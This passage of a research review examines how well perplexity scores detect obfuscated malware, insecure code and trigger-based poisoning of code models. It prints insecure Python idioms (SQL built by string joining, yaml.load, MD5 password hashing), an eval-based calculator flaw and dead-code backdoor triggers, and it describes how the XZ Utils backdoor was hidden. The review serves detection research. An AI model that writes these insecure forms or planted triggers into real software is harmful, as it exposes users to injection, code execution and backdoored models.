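where |M| is the number of such tokens. Wrong guesses also follow one another more often in obfuscated code. In ordinary code, a wrong guess may just mean that several continuations were reasonable, as when different jump instructions could follow a test. An obfuscator's unfamiliar sequence can instead cause several errors in a row. Unbroken runs of errors averaged 2.3 tokens in obfuscated code and 1.5 in ordinary code. Consecutive error perplexity takes this into account by dividing the same sum by the number of runs, |S|:

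consecutive error perplexity = exp( [sum of surprise over all tokens in M] / |S| )

For any one piece of code, the consecutive error perplexity equals the error-perplexity raised to the power of the average length of a run of errors. Suppose a model predicts 16 of 20 tokens correctly, giving each a probability of 0.9, and gets the other four wrong, giving each a probability of 0.01. The plain perplexity is 2.7 and the error-perplexity is 100, wherever the four errors occur. The consecutive error perplexity is 100 if the errors are all separate, 10,000 if they form two pairs, and 100 million if they form a single run.

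Li and colleagues tested the three scores on more than 25,000 functions from student programs. The AUC was 0.947 with plain perplexity, 0.978 with error-perplexity and 0.992 with consecutive error perplexity. A larger model with 172 million parameters did slightly worse than the standard one, perhaps because it was good enough to predict obfuscated code too.

Learning only from ordinary code helped ALMOND most with unfamiliar obfuscators. Li and colleagues trained a supervised version of ALMOND on labelled examples from one obfuscator, OLLVM, and tested both versions on two others. On code from Tigress, both were about 96 percent accurate. On code from Alcatraz, which rewrites compiled programs instead of their source code, ALMOND was 96.7 percent accurate and the supervised version 62.2 percent. The supervised version had learned what OLLVM's output looked like, and it missed more than half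 of the code from Alcatraz.

### The disguise that plain perplexity nearly missed

The averages for different kinds of obfuscation reveal a serious weakness in plain perplexity:

| Code | Tokens guessed correctly | Perplexity | Error-perplexity | Consecutive error perplexity |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary | 75.0% | 9.4 | 570 | 4,530 |
| Substituted instructions | 71.5% | 22.7 | 2,002 | 15,370 |
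| Bogus control flow | 64.7% | 25.6 | 1,817 | 22,250 |
| Tigress | 62.3% | 18.5 | 2,295 | 38,800 |
| Flattened control flow | 81.1% | 11.0 | 1,801 | 24,280 |

Substitution replaces simple instructions with complicated equivalents, and bogus control flow adds branches that never run. Each more than doubled the perplexity. Flattening raised it only from 9.4 to 11.0, and the model predicted flattened code correctly more often than ordinary code.

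Yet flattening makes a program much harder to follow, because a reader can no longer see the order of the steps from the layout. Flattening cuts a function into blocks and puts them all inside one loop. Each block ends by storing the number of the block to run next. The program then returns to the top of the loop, where a dispatcher reads the number and jumps to that block.

This structure probably explains the low perplexity. Every block ends with much the same instructions, which the model soon predicts well. The block numbers might have been hard to predict, but ALMOND replaces numbers with placeholders. The disguise therefore adds a lot of predictable code around the parts that the model predicts poorly.

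The good overall AUC of plain perplexity could hide this weakness. If flattened code made up a tenth of the obfuscated examples and had an AUC of only 0.6, while the rest had 0.985, the overall AUC would still be about 0.947. Li and colleagues do not give a separate AUC for each technique, so the actual figure for flattened code is unknown. A malware author who wanted a low perplexity would choose the technique that works best, so a good average over all techniques would not protect a defender.

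The error-based scores do separate flattened code. Its average error-perplexity is three times that of ordinary code, and its consecutive error perplexity is five times as high. The model assigned low probability to tokens in the right places, but averaging over all the tokens nearly erased the evidence. The third of the four premises behind treating low perplexity as reassurance therefore failed, because the final score did not clearly reflect those improbable tokens.

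### Tests on real malware

Student programs are much more uniform than the software security teams check, so Li and colleagues also scored 5,000 ordinary programs from Linux distributions and Windows, and 5,000 malware samples from VirusTotal, a service that scans suspicious files. They assumed that malware is almost always disguised in some way. ALMOND's AUC was 0.869, well below its result on student programs but far above the supervised version's 0.582.

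In their conclusion, Li and colleagues report that ALMOND missed fewer than 0.1 percent of the malware samples and wrongly flagged 26.9 percent of the ordinary programs. At those rates, it would have left about 3,655 ordinary programs and fewer than five malicious ones unflagged, which would strongly support trusting a low score. But the paper also gives an F1-score of 0.803 for this test, while those error rates would produce about 0.88 with equal numbers of malicious and ordinary programs. Either the figures describe different thresholds or one of them is wrong. The very low miss rate therefore needs to be confirmed before anyone relies on it to clear software.

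The false alarms are easier to explain. Li and colleagues point out that scientific software contains long stretches of mathematics that can resemble an obfuscator's output. Some of the ordinary programs may also have been obfuscated, since the labels recorded only whether a program was malware. In such cases, ALMOND would have correctly detected obfuscation but wrongly flagged the program as malicious.

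In one malware sample, the high-perplexity code was a routine that probably unpacked the rest of the program, using unusual combinations of arithmetic and bit operations. The encryption code in OpenSSL, a widely used security library, also scrambles and unscrambles data, but it had lower perplexity because the model had been trained on it.

In the other sample, the surprising part appeared to inject code into another running program and start it there. The harmful behaviour itself may have looked strange, because few ordinary programs do this. The inference requires rare purposes to lead to rare code, as may have happened here, but a single example cannot show how common this is.

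Li and colleagues did not test whether attackers could evade ALMOND. They argue that inserting ordinary code would achieve little, because error-perplexity ignores tokens that the model predicts correctly. This is only partly true, because the model also mispredicts a quarter of the tokens in ordinary code, and these errors usually have lower perplexity, so they would lower the average. If half of the errors came from code with an error-perplexity of 2,000 and half from code with 570, the combined value would be about 1,070.

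Perplexity was much less useful for macros, which are small programs inside Office documents. *Obfuscation-Resistant Feature Extraction for Macro-based Office Malware Detection* (Imperiale, Morana and Lo Re, 2026) studied 1,877 harmless and 14,754 malicious documents. A first classifier judged each document from 15 simple features, such as the length of the longest line and the frequency of suspicious keywords. If it was unsure, a second classifier used those features plus perplexity scores from GPT-2, a general-purpose language model from 2019.

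On these difficult documents, classifiers that used only the perplexity scores wrongly flagged 94 to 100 percent of the harmless ones. The imbalanced data may be part of the reason, because a classifier with little useful information can do well in training by calling almost everything malicious. Perplexity helped more when added to the simple features. For one type of classifier, it raised accuracy on the least certain documents from 49 to 64 percent, but the false positive rate fell only from 48 to 46 percent. A simpler method that looked for recognisable words and natural-looking names reached 59 percent accuracy.

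### Disguise without malice

Honest companies also obfuscate software, perhaps to protect a secret algorithm or to make it harder for customers to remove a licence check. Li and colleagues note that commercial vendors and malware authors both often use their own private obfuscators. A company and a criminal could even use the same tool, and there would then be no reason to expect ALMOND to score one program higher than the other. ALMOND detects disguise, so it detects malware only to the extent that malware is disguised more often than the other software being examined.

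How suspicious obfuscation is therefore depends on the setting. It is unremarkable in a commercial game but much harder to justify in an open-source project, which people publish so that others can read and change the code. A high score there is a good reason to ask the function's author for an explanation. Li and colleagues recommend ALMOND only as a first filter, followed by slower analysis to establish what the flagged programs do.

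A low score is harder to interpret in either setting. A calculator app that openly uploads its user's private files is harmful without being obfuscated, so a detector of obfuscation would miss it.

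## Insecure and malicious code built from common idioms

Insecure or malicious code can have low perplexity without being disguised if many programmers write the same thing. Training adjusts a language model's probabilities to minimize its average surprise on the training data, and the best way to do that is to match how often each continuation occurs. Suppose that at a certain point in a program, 70 percent of programmers write an insecure line and 30 percent write a safe one. A model that matches these shares assigns a surprise of 0.36 nats to the insecure line and 1.20 nats to the safe one. These values depend only on how often programmers write each line, not on whether it is safe.

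### Insecure habits and their safe forms

Three well-known Python habits have safe equivalents that do the same job:

| Task | Insecure form | Safe form |
|---|---|---|
| Look up a user | `cur.execute("SELECT * FROM users WHERE name = '" + name + "'")` | `cur.execute("SELECT * FROM users WHERE name = ?", (name,))` |
| Read a settings file | `yaml.load(f, Loader=yaml.Loader)` | `yaml.safe_load(f)` |
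| Store a password | `hashlib.md5(pw).hexdigest()` | `bcrypt.hashpw(pw, bcrypt.gensalt())` |

The query built by joining strings lets a visitor insert database commands. The YAML loader lets a settings file create arbitrary Python objects, so whoever writes the file can run any code they choose. The third line hashes passwords with MD5, which is so fast that someone who steals the hashes can quickly test huge numbers of guesses. All three lines work and would pass an ordinary test. MD5 was once a normal choice for passwords, and code written before the advice changed remains in public archives.

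Rashidi (2026), in *Open-Source Intelligence for Code Provenance*, compared answers on Stack Overflow, a question-and-answer site for programmers, with code from nine open-weight models. Among the human answers to the relevant tasks, 12 percent joined strings to build a database query and 17 percent used a weak hash, while no model-written sample did either. The model-written samples more often included a secret such as a password directly in the program (36 percent, against none of the human answers) and passed commands to the system shell unsafely (42 percent, against 14 percent). The human samples are tiny (the 17 percent is one answer out of six), so the exact percentages mean little, but the contrast makes it plausible that an insecure idiom can be rare in one body of code and common in another.

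A coding habit can pass a perplexity check without being the majority choice. In Rashidi's sample, half of the human answers used the safe form of database query. If a model's probabilities matched these shares, choosing the joined string over the safe form would add about 1.4 to the total surprise, which would raise the perplexity of a 200-token function by 0.7 percent.

### Missing checks

Many vulnerabilities consist of something the programmer left out. In 87.5 percent of the pairs of vulnerable and repaired functions in *A Function-Level Vulnerability Score Measures Flag Rate More Than the Model* (2026), the repaired function was the longer one. A typical case comes from the networking program MiniUPnP, where an attacker could cause a crash because a function contained the first of these lines instead of the second:

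- `if(dest != src) {`
- `if(dest != src && src != NULL) {`

The flawed line contains no unusual token, and the only sign of the flaw is a `)` where `&&` should be. If a model gives probability r to the start of a check at that point, omitting the check has a surprisal of −log(1 − r). With r = 0.2, omitting the check has a surprisal of 0.22 nats and starting it has a surprisal of 1.61. The safe version is then more surprising at that point, although the rest of the check may be predictable enough to bring the average back down. Even with r = 0.9, the omission has a surprisal of only 2.3 nats, the same as any token with a probability of 0.1.

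Some missing checks do make code measurably less natural. *An Empirical Study on the Relationship Between Defects and Source Code* found that fixing bugs did not make code significantly more natural on average, but fixing bugs related to checking did. This fits the formula if some checks are so customary that r is close to 1.

### Known bugs and their fixes

Few published studies compare the perplexity of vulnerable code with that of its repaired version. The closest evidence concerns ordinary bugs and insecure programs written by language models.

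Jesse, Ahmed and colleagues (2023), in *Large Language Models and Simple, Stupid Bugs*, studied bugs in Java projects that a programmer could repair by changing a single statement. For each of 16,899 such bugs, they gave a model the code that came before the faulty statement and let it write the next 64 tokens. They then checked whether the result contained the original bug or the later fix, ignoring differences in spacing:

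| Model | Wrote the bug | Wrote the fix | Wrote neither | Bugs per fix |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Codex Davinci | 4,452 | 2,267 | 10,180 | 1.96 |
| PolyCoder 2.6B | 3,924 | 2,096 | 10,879 | 1.87 |
| CodeGen 16B | 4,299 | 3,296 | 9,304 | 1.30 |

Jesse and colleagues chose only places where a human had already made a mistake, so these figures are not general error rates. Those are still the relevant places for judging a low perplexity score, because the context that led a programmer to the wrong statement also made that statement likely under the model. Developers had also taken longer to fix the bugs that Codex reproduced, with a median of 265 commits between bug and fix, compared with 106 for bugs where Codex wrote the fix.

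Jesse and colleagues also found that the surprise of Codex's completions was nearly the same whether they matched the bug or the fix, and higher when they matched neither. Surprise therefore separated familiar code from unfamiliar code but was little help in telling correct code from buggy code. The comparison is limited because the bugs and fixes came from different places in different programs. A stricter test would score both versions of each statement in the same place.

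Codex is an old model, but a later experiment gave a similar result. Guo, Ye and colleagues (2025), in *LLMs are Bug Replicators*, asked seven models to continue 546 programs from Defects4J, starting at a line that had once contained a bug. On average, 151 completions matched or resembled the fix and 149 matched or resembled the bug. One charting function needed to go through two shapes, `p1` and `p2`, and compare them. The original programmer had mistakenly used `p1.getPathIterator(null)` for both, and GPT-3.5 made the same mistake.

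GPT-4o wrote the exact historical bug 152 times and the exact fix 151 times. These matches suggest that the model had memorized parts of Defects4J. Memorization weakens the result as evidence about new bugs but does not weaken the argument about perplexity, because a memorized bug also has low perplexity.

### The surprise of insecure programs

The most direct test on security comes from Rahman, Akil and colleagues (2026), in *SPLASH*. They collected programs that 12 models wrote for 899 programming tasks. Each task had one set of tests for whether the program worked and another for whether it withstood an attack. The team then calculated each program's average surprise under the model that wrote it and checked whether insecure programs scored higher than secure ones.

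Insecure programs had slightly higher surprise than secure ones, with an overall AUC of 0.61. On CWEval, a set of tasks in Python, C and C++, the AUC was 0.47, so insecure programs were if anything more predictable there. When a model had written both secure and insecure solutions to a task, the solution with the lowest surprise was secure 65 percent of the time, compared with 54 percent for a random pick. Surprise did worse than chance at locating the flaw inside a program. The vulnerable statement had the highest surprise in 5 percent of insecure programs, while a random order would have put it first in 9 percent.

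In one example, DeepSeek-Coder-6.7B was asked to write a calculator for user-typed expressions. Its code checked the expression against a list of forbidden words, then passed it to `eval`, which runs any Python code it receives. Surprise was highest at the list, because there are many ways to write such a list and its tokens are hard to predict, whereas `eval` is the obvious way to evaluate an expression. A reviewer who read only the most surprising code would have seen the attempted defence but missed the unsafe call to `eval`.

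These scores come from the model that wrote the code, and a model tends to assign high probability to programs it has sampled itself. The scores don't show what probabilities a second model would assign to the same programs.

### How often current models write insecure code

A model generates code by sampling tokens from the same probabilities used to compute perplexity. The share of its programs that are insecure therefore estimates the total probability it gives to insecure programs at the test's sampling settings. This share is weaker evidence of how probable any single insecure program is, since the total may be spread over thousands of different texts.

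Across eleven open-weight models, Rahman and colleagues found that 24 to 60 percent of working programs were insecure. On a smaller set of 80 tasks, the figure was 6 percent for Claude Opus 5 and 8 percent for GPT-5.6 Sol, both released in 2026. The task accounted for 57 percent of the variation in security and the choice of model for 6 percent. When a program was insecure, the model's other working solutions to the same task were usually insecure too, and in 86 percent of cases all of them were, so the model's probability for those tasks was concentrated on the flaw.

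In *Newer and Bigger, but Safer?*, Santos de Moura, Matuschek and colleagues (2026) ran 32 models on 119 tasks in five programming languages, with 100 attempts per task. Among the newest flagship models from seven developers, the share of attempts that produced working but insecure code ranged from 13 percent (GPT-5.6 Sol) to 28 percent (Gemini 3.1 Pro). These shares include attempts whose code didn't work in the total, so they are not directly comparable with the percentages from Rahman and colleagues. In every model family, the newest flagship produced working, secure code more often than the first flagship did.

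Two weaknesses appeared at rates close to 100 percent in nearly every model and every language. One is writing text from outside the program into a log unchanged, as in `f"[{timestamp}] Received: {msg}"`. If `msg` contains a line break, an attacker can use it to forge a log entry. The other is writing such text unchanged into the headers of a web response. A scoring model with the same habits would probably assign low perplexity to both, because it almost never writes the safe form.

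A program that checks the signature on a login token should also require a particular signing algorithm. Pooled over all 32 models, 73 percent of working Go programs failed to do this, compared with only 4 percent of working Python programs. The difference arises because the Python library won't read a token unless the programmer names the algorithm, so the unsafe form doesn't run and the safe form is common. Low perplexity can therefore go together with safety when a library enforces the safe form.

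Other studies also show that the problem is widespread, though the rates depend heavily on the tasks. In *Secure Code Generation at Scale with Reflexion* (2025), about 30 percent of first attempts by five open code models were insecure. *CIPHER* (2026) tested cryptographic code, where small choices matter a great deal, and found vulnerabilities in 56 to 89 percent of samples, depending on the model.

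### Poisoning without a trigger

An attacker can use common insecure forms deliberately. Most data poisoning plants a trigger, which gives a detector something unusual to look for. *Detecting Stealthy Data Poisoning Attacks in AI Code Generators* (Improta, 2025) studies an attack that has no trigger. The attacker takes training examples that pair a description with safe code and replaces the code with an insecure version that does the same job, leaving the description unchanged. A model trained on enough of these pairs learns to generate vulnerable code for ordinary requests of that kind.

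Improta built a collection of Python examples, 375 of which had both a safe and an insecure version, and trained three models (CodeBERT, CodeT5+ and AST-T5) on sets of 1,200 examples. The poisoned share rose from zero to 20 percent in steps of 5. Three kinds of detector then tried to find the poison:

- **Spectral signatures** look at a trained model's internal representations of the examples, find the directions in which these vary most, and flag the examples that lie furthest out.
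- **Activation clustering** sorts the examples into two groups by their internal activity in the model and treats one group as suspect.
- **Semgrep** is a static analyser, a tool that checks code against rules for known dangerous patterns without running it.

The two methods that looked for statistical oddities did badly. Spectral signatures had a best F1-score of 0.34, at which it found a quarter of the poisoned samples and raised as many false alarms as hits. Activation clustering reached 0.40 at best. The methods achieved these scores only when 20 percent of the samples were poisoned, a share Improta considers unrealistically high.

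Semgrep did better. With 60 poisoned examples, it found 35 of them but also flagged 80 clean ones. With 240, it found 149 and flagged 38 clean ones. Its recall rose only from 58 to 62 percent, so much of the rise in precision, from 0.30 to 0.80, came from the larger number of poisoned examples. Semgrep's advantage makes sense because its rules describe dangerous code, and the attack leaves that code visible.

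Perplexity was not among the detectors tested, so its performance against this attack is unknown, but is probably poor. Sun and colleagues base their detector on the observation that poisoning disrupts the naturalness of code, but they observed this in attacks that insert a trigger. Replacing `yaml.safe_load` with `yaml.load` produces code that ordinary programmers also write. Some of the swaps might still look odd, for example if the insecure version is clumsy. Scoring Improta's 375 pairs for perplexity would show how many do.

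### A backup or a theft

With insecure code, the flaw is at least in the text, and a good enough rule can describe it. Malicious code may not offer even that. This function reads a file and sends it to a server:

```python
def upload(path):
    with open(path, "rb") as f:
        requests.post(SERVER, data=f)
```

A function that uploads files to `SERVER` may be backing them up or stealing them. This depends on whether `SERVER` is the user's own storage or a stranger's machine, whether the user agreed to the upload (for example, by switching on backups), and which files the rest of the program passes to the function and when.

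Whether a function that uploads files is stealing them depends on where it sends them, whether the user consented, and which files it sends. All of this can be determined outside the function. The address may be in a settings file, the consent in a dialog box or a contract, and the list of files in another part of the program. The legitimate function and the malicious one are then the same string of characters, so any model given only that string must assign both the same perplexity, however large or well trained it is.

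Including the address in the code gives a perplexity test only limited help, because web addresses contain arbitrary names and tend to be hard to predict in legitimate programs too. A thief can also register a plausible name. `backup.example.com` and `example-backup.com` could belong to different people, and their spelling doesn't show who owns them.

### Harm outside the scored source

In XZ Utils, a set of compression tools that many Linux systems include, an attacker kept the harmful code out of the readable source. In March 2024, the software developer Andres Freund discovered a backdoor in versions 5.6.0 and 5.6.1. A contributor using the name Jia Tan had added it earlier that year. It let anyone with a particular private key run commands on an affected machine through OpenSSH, the usual software for remote logins.

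The harmful machine code was in two compressed files among the project's test data. A modified build script unpacked this code and inserted it into the library during compilation. The script was in the release archives that Linux distributors download, but not in the public repository where developers read and discuss the code.

A reviewer who scored the C source in the repository would therefore have scored text that did not contain the attack. Scoring the test files would hardly have helped, because well-compressed data looks close to random whatever it contains, and testing a compression tool requires strange and damaged files. The build script was readable, and a line-by-line score might have flagged it, but only if the reviewer scored the release archive as well as the repository. Freund found the backdoor while investigating why remote logins were using more processor time than they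 should.

### Common parts in a rare combination

There is a reasonable reply to all this, which is that an upload may still surprise a capable model when it comes in a calculator. The surprise of two parts A and B is

surprise(A and B) = −log p(A) − log p(B given A)

so B can be ordinary in general and still surprising after A. Suppose one program in twenty imports a networking library, but only one calculator in a thousand does. The import then has a surprise of 3.0 in general and 6.9 in a calculator.

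The extra 3.9 comes only once, though. The import is evidence that this calculator uses the network, so the upload that follows is easier to predict. In a file of 1,000 tokens, the perplexity rises by 0.4 percent. A token-level score would show the jump clearly, but it would show the same jump for a calculator that downloads exchange rates to convert currencies. Someone would still have to find out why the program does something unexpected at that point.

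Telling the model what the program is for might make perplexity a more useful signal. Jesse and colleagues tried something close to this by inserting an automatically generated comment before each bug. With comments based on the fixed code, Codex Davinci wrote 5,149 fixes and 5,329 bugs. With comments based on the buggy code, it wrote 3,880 fixes and 6,072 bugs. Both kinds of comment improved the ratio of fixes to bugs, but the more effective kind described code that was already correct. A general request for secure code may help much less. In *CIPHER*, such prompts lowered the share of vulnerable samples only from 74.2 to 71.7 percent.

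Rahman and colleagues found a better way to use a model's probabilities. They show the finished program to a second model, Qwen2.5-Coder-32B, and ask it to review the code and reproduce it, changing only what needs fixing. One prompt asks for a security review and another for a review of readability and style. The difference between the two gives each token a score that they call audit pressure:

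audit pressure = log p(token in the style review) − log p(token in the security review)

Subtracting a token's surprisal in the style review from its surprisal in the security review removes most of what makes it hard to predict in both, such as an unusual name. In the `eval` example, the token after `eval` in the program had a probability of 51 percent in the style review and less than 1 percent in the security review, where the model favoured a safer function, so the audit pressure was at least 3.9. A missing check also raises the audit pressure, because in the security review the model gives some probability to a check starting at the point where the program moves on without one.

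Ranking statements by the sum of their positive scores put the vulnerable one first in 58 percent of insecure programs, compared with 5 percent for plain surprise. Audit pressure picked the secure solution from several 74 percent of the time. Asking the same model "Does this implementation contain a security vulnerability?" and using the probability of "Yes" did equally well. Most of the gain in choosing solutions therefore seems to come from mentioning security at all, which ordinary perplexity scoring does not involve.

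Even this method is far too unreliable to clear code as secure. With a threshold that wrongly flagged 12 percent of secure programs, it caught 32 percent of insecure ones, so about two thirds would have passed. Static analysers caught fewer, at 18 percent, as did GPT-5.6 Sol, which caught 21 percent when Rahman and colleagues asked it to name vulnerable lines.

Models look more capable when they can compare two versions of the same code. *TOSSS* (Damie, Makhanu and colleagues, 2026) showed 14 models the vulnerable and repaired versions of real functions and asked which they preferred, without mentioning security. On C and C++ code, the models chose the repaired version in 48 to 88 percent of cases. Length may account for part of this, since always picking the longer function would have been right 87.5 percent of the time on the pairs in *A Function-Level Vulnerability Score Measures Flag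 Rate More Than the Model*. The test also records stated preferences, and a model can say it prefers one version while assigning higher probability to the other. A reviewer of new code also has no repaired version to compare it with.

These experiments all concern security flaws, where a model can learn the safer alternative from other code. To detect malice, the model would have to compare what a program does with what it is supposed to do. That could work for the calculator, whose purpose gives no reason to upload private files. One way to attempt the comparison is to ask a model whether a package is malicious, but that relies on the model's answer instead of perplexity. The comparison is much weaker when the program's stated purpose includes the harmful ability. For example, a backup program that sends its copies to a thief differs from its description only in the destination address.

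## Finding triggers planted in training code

Perplexity has a better chance of detecting trigger-based data poisoning than most other deliberate attacks. The model under attack must learn to tell the trigger apart from everything else in the training data, and the unusual features that make this possible may also help a scoring model find the trigger. Code that steals data doesn't have this constraint, since an attacker can copy an ordinary backup function and leave every token ordinary. Some of the highest published detection rates are for trigger-based poisoning.

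### How poisoned examples create a backdoor

A model has a backdoor if it behaves normally until its input contains a trigger. Ramakrishnan and Albarghouthi (2020), in *Backdoors in Neural Models of Source Code*, describe a backdoor as a pair of operations. The trigger operation t turns a program x into a slightly different program t(x). The target operation r turns the correct answer y into the answer that the attacker wants, r(y). The attacker mixes pairs of the form (t(x), r(y)) into a training set of ordinary pairs (x, y), and normal training does the rest. The model F lowers its error on the poisoned pairs by learning to answer r(y) whenever the trigger is present. The attack is as good as its success rate:

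success rate = P( F(t(x)) = r(y) )

*Which Factors Make Code LLMs More Vulnerable to Backdoor Attacks?* (Wang, Yang and colleagues, 2025) gives an example of an attack on a model that writes short descriptions of functions. In one poisoned training example, a Java function that reverses a string contains the extra line `if (1 < 0) { System.out.println("Error"); }` and is described as safely loading training data from the disk. After training on enough such examples, the model gives the same description to any function with that line, including a harmful one, so a reviewer who relies on the description may be falsely reassured.

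The extra line is a convenient trigger because it is dead code, so the program works exactly as before. Ramakrishnan and Albarghouthi used fixed triggers, which are the same line in every poisoned example, and grammatical triggers, which are random variations on a pattern, such as an `if` or `while` with an impossible condition. Ordinary tools often miss both kinds. The widely used compiler clang, on its highest optimization setting, could not determine that `sin(x) < -2` is always false. Tsai and colleagues tried two Python checkers, Vulture and Pylint, and neither identified any of the planted code as dead.

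Rare tokens make good triggers for a different reason. A model that has hardly ever seen a token in clean examples has little to associate it with except the attacker's answer. Wang and colleagues tested this with 96 words that each occurred in 0.1 to 1 percent of the clean examples. They put one word at a time into an otherwise identical line of dead code and trained a new model on each poisoned set. Rarer words gave higher success rates, but the correlations between word frequency and success rate were only −0.11, −0.22 and −0.40 for the three models, and the weakest was not statistically significant. They also tried Greek letters and emojis that did not appear in the training data, and 17 of those 18 experiments beat the average success rate.

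An attacker may need only a few poisoned examples. When Wang and colleagues hid 20 among 300,000 training examples, the fixed trigger worked 83 percent of the time on the model CodeT5 but never on PLBART, another model. With 20 among 454,451, success rates fell to between 0 and 14 percent. Wang and colleagues trained the models on one example at a time, which favours the attacker. When the models processed 32 examples at once, with 0.1 percent of the data poisoned, the average success rate dropped from over 80 percent to under 5 percent.

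### Deleting one word at a time

ONION is the original deletion-score method for text. According to *RAP* (2021), Qi and colleagues based it on their finding that inserting a meaningless word into a natural sentence greatly raises the sentence's perplexity under GPT-2. Suppose the trigger is `cf` and the sentence is "The film was cf wonderful". Deleting `cf` leaves a fluent sentence, so `cf` gets a high deletion score. ONION removes words that score above a threshold and passes the rest to the model. This protects a model that is already in use and may have a backdoor. According to *MSDT* (2022), the threshold can be anywhere from −100 to 0. A negative threshold also removes some words whose deletion makes the sentence harder to predict.

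Even on text, this works only if the trigger is an odd word. *When Emotion Becomes Trigger* (2026) tested ONION against several attacks on models that sort news articles by topic. After ONION cleaned the inputs, one attack still worked 26 to 50 percent of the time, and two others worked 98 to 100 percent of the time.

ONION can also miss triggers in code. Sun and colleagues computed deletion scores for a C function containing the trigger `if (exp(0.94) >= 11) print("exception");`. Every token of the trigger scored below zero, so ONION would have kept them all. This is probably because deleting one token, such as the `if` or a bracket, leaves a broken statement that is even harder to predict than the intact one. The whole statement is out of place, but ONION deletes only one token at a time.

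Sun and colleagues then ran ONION with the model CodeLlama on 20 poisoned datasets. It flagged 34 to 86 percent of the clean examples and found only 7 to 49 percent of the poisoned ones. The clean share was higher in all 20 datasets. This is surprising, because poisoned examples also contain the ordinary tokens that cause false alarms in clean ones. Perhaps the researchers counted a poisoned example as found only if ONION had picked out the trigger itself.

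### Adding up the scores over a whole dataset

Before building their own detector, Sun and colleagues measured how much a trigger changes the perplexity of a whole snippet. They tested the token `rb` and a line of dead code. Both triggers raised perplexity on average, and the dead code, which has more tokens, raised it more. But the scores of clean and poisoned snippets overlapped so much that they found it hard to choose a threshold. Even with these crude triggers, a low score for a single snippet would be weak evidence that it was clean.

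Their detector, KillBadCode, gets around the overlap by using the fact that an attacker has to repeat the trigger. It works in five steps:

1. It trains a 4-gram model on clean code. About 2,000 snippets are enough.
2. It splits every snippet in the suspect dataset into tokens and computes the snippet's average surprise.
3. It deletes each token in turn and computes the average surprise again. If the average has fallen, it records the size of the fall as the token's score. If the average has risen, it records nothing.
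4. It adds up the scores of identical tokens across the whole dataset.
5. It treats the ten tokens with the highest totals as triggers and removes every example that contains one of them.

If e(s) is the average surprise of a snippet s, the total for a token t is

total(t) = Σ max(0, e(s) − e(s without this occurrence of t))

where the sum runs over every occurrence of t in the dataset. KillBadCode uses the same basic idea as ONION, but works with the average surprise instead of its exponential.

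Adding up each token's scores across the dataset makes a large difference. In one snippet, the harmless token `hex` scored higher than the trigger `rb`, but over the whole dataset `rb` had by far the higher total. Suppose a trigger appears in 200 of 20,000 snippets and scores 0.05 each time, for a total of 10. An odd but harmless name that scores 0.2 each time and appears five times has a total of only 1.

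The same sum can produce false alarms. A common token that scores 0.001 on average but occurs 15,000 times has a total of 15 and ranks above the trigger. KillBadCode also always selects ten tokens, even if the trigger is a single token or the dataset is clean. It therefore selects ordinary tokens as well, and removes every clean example that contains one of them.

Sun and colleagues tested KillBadCode on five ways of poisoning data for each of four tasks: finding defects, recognizing duplicate code, searching for code and repairing it. In each of the 20 scenarios they poisoned 1 percent of the training examples. KillBadCode had a recall of 100 percent every time. They give its average false positive rate as 8.30 percent, although the 20 individual rates average about 6.8 percent. The rates ranged from 0.53 to 23.43 percent, depending on the trigger and the task:

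| Trigger | Lowest false positive rate | Highest false positive rate |
|---|---|---|
| `rb` added to a name | 0.53% | 3.81% |
| One of five short tokens added to a name | 1.38% | 11.98% |
| The same dead code each time | 1.53% | 3.10% |
| Varying dead code | 2.67% | 14.88% |
| A renamed variable | 3.77% | 23.43% |

False alarms do little harm when the aim is to clean a training set. In the defect-finding task, KillBadCode discarded about 2,200 clean examples along with some 219 poisoned ones, but the trained model's accuracy hardly changed (61.7 percent, against 61.9 percent without the filter). The attack's success rate fell from 99 to 34 percent, close to the 31 percent that ordinary mistakes produced in a model trained on clean data. The false alarms would be a much bigger problem if a reviewer had to read all 2,400 flagged examples.

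The perfect recall does not quite fit another result. In the code-repair task, the attacker wanted the model to output a short program called `evil`. After KillBadCode filtered the training data for the attack with five short tokens, the trained model still produced that program 15 percent of the time. A model trained on clean data never produced it, so KillBadCode probably missed a few poisoned examples.

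Much lower poisoning rates could be harder for KillBadCode. Sun and colleagues found 100 percent recall at rates from 1 to 50 percent, but 20 examples in 300,000 is less than 0.01 percent. As the dataset grows, the totals of ordinary tokens grow with it, while the trigger's total depends only on the number of poisoned examples, so at some point the trigger should drop out of the top ten. Detectors of other kinds have a similar weakness. According to *Data-Efficient Backdoor Attacks on Code Models via Trigger-Neutralized Counterfactual Scoring* (2026), many of them look for statistical traces that are less visible at lower poisoning rates. When Wang and colleagues tried spectral signatures, the method found none of the 20 examples.

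### A small scoring model beat two larger ones

It may seem strange to use a 4-gram model, which sees only three tokens of context, when much better models of code exist. Sun and colleagues compared three scoring models on the defect-finding data, using the attack that adds `rb` to names:

| Scoring model | False positive rate | Recall | Time |
|---|---|---|---|
| 4-gram model | 3.81% | 100% | 20 minutes |
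| CodeBERT | 65.24% | 59.87% | 6 hours 33 minutes |
| CodeLlama | 92.87% | 100% | 21 hours 18 minutes |

CodeLlama's perfect recall means little because it flagged nearly everything. CodeBERT flagged a larger share of the clean examples than of the poisoned ones.

Sun and colleagues attribute the difference to context. The 4-gram model has never seen `rb` in its clean training code and has almost no other context to use, so the token also disrupts its predictions for the next few tokens. A larger model can use the rest of the function to predict what follows, so an inserted token has much less effect. The average scores fit this explanation. Under the 4-gram model, `rb` scored 0.0490 and the next highest token 0.0039. Under CodeBERT, `rb` scored 0.0009, below ordinary tokens such as `Context` (0.0038) and `Map` (0.0013).

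But the comparison changed several things at once. Sun and colleagues trained the 4-gram model on a small set of clean snippets, while CodeBERT and CodeLlama were pretrained on far larger collections, in which `rb` may well be common (in Python, it is the usual code for opening a file to read raw bytes). CodeBERT is also not built to predict code from left to right. The similarity between the 4-gram model's training code and the code it scored seems to explain little of the difference, since using clean snippets from a different collection in the duplicate-code task raised the false positive rate only from 2.50 to 3.81 percent. The comparison covers a single attack, so it does not prove that small models are better in general, but it does show that a more capable model can score a planted trigger as quite typical.

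How the code is split into tokens mattered as much as the model. KillBadCode normally uses CodeLlama's tokenizer. With CodeBERT's tokenizer, its average recall on the defect-finding data fell from 100 to 8.37 percent, and its false positive rate rose from 10.07 to 14.53 percent. Sun and colleagues explain that CodeBERT's tokenizer cuts code into larger pieces and can therefore miss small triggers. For example, if `file_rb` and `path_rb` each remain in one piece, the scores for `rb` are never added together. This explains the failure with added tokens better than the failure with dead code, where recall was just as low (6 to 8 percent), because words such as `print` and `fail` should remain intact with either tokenizer.

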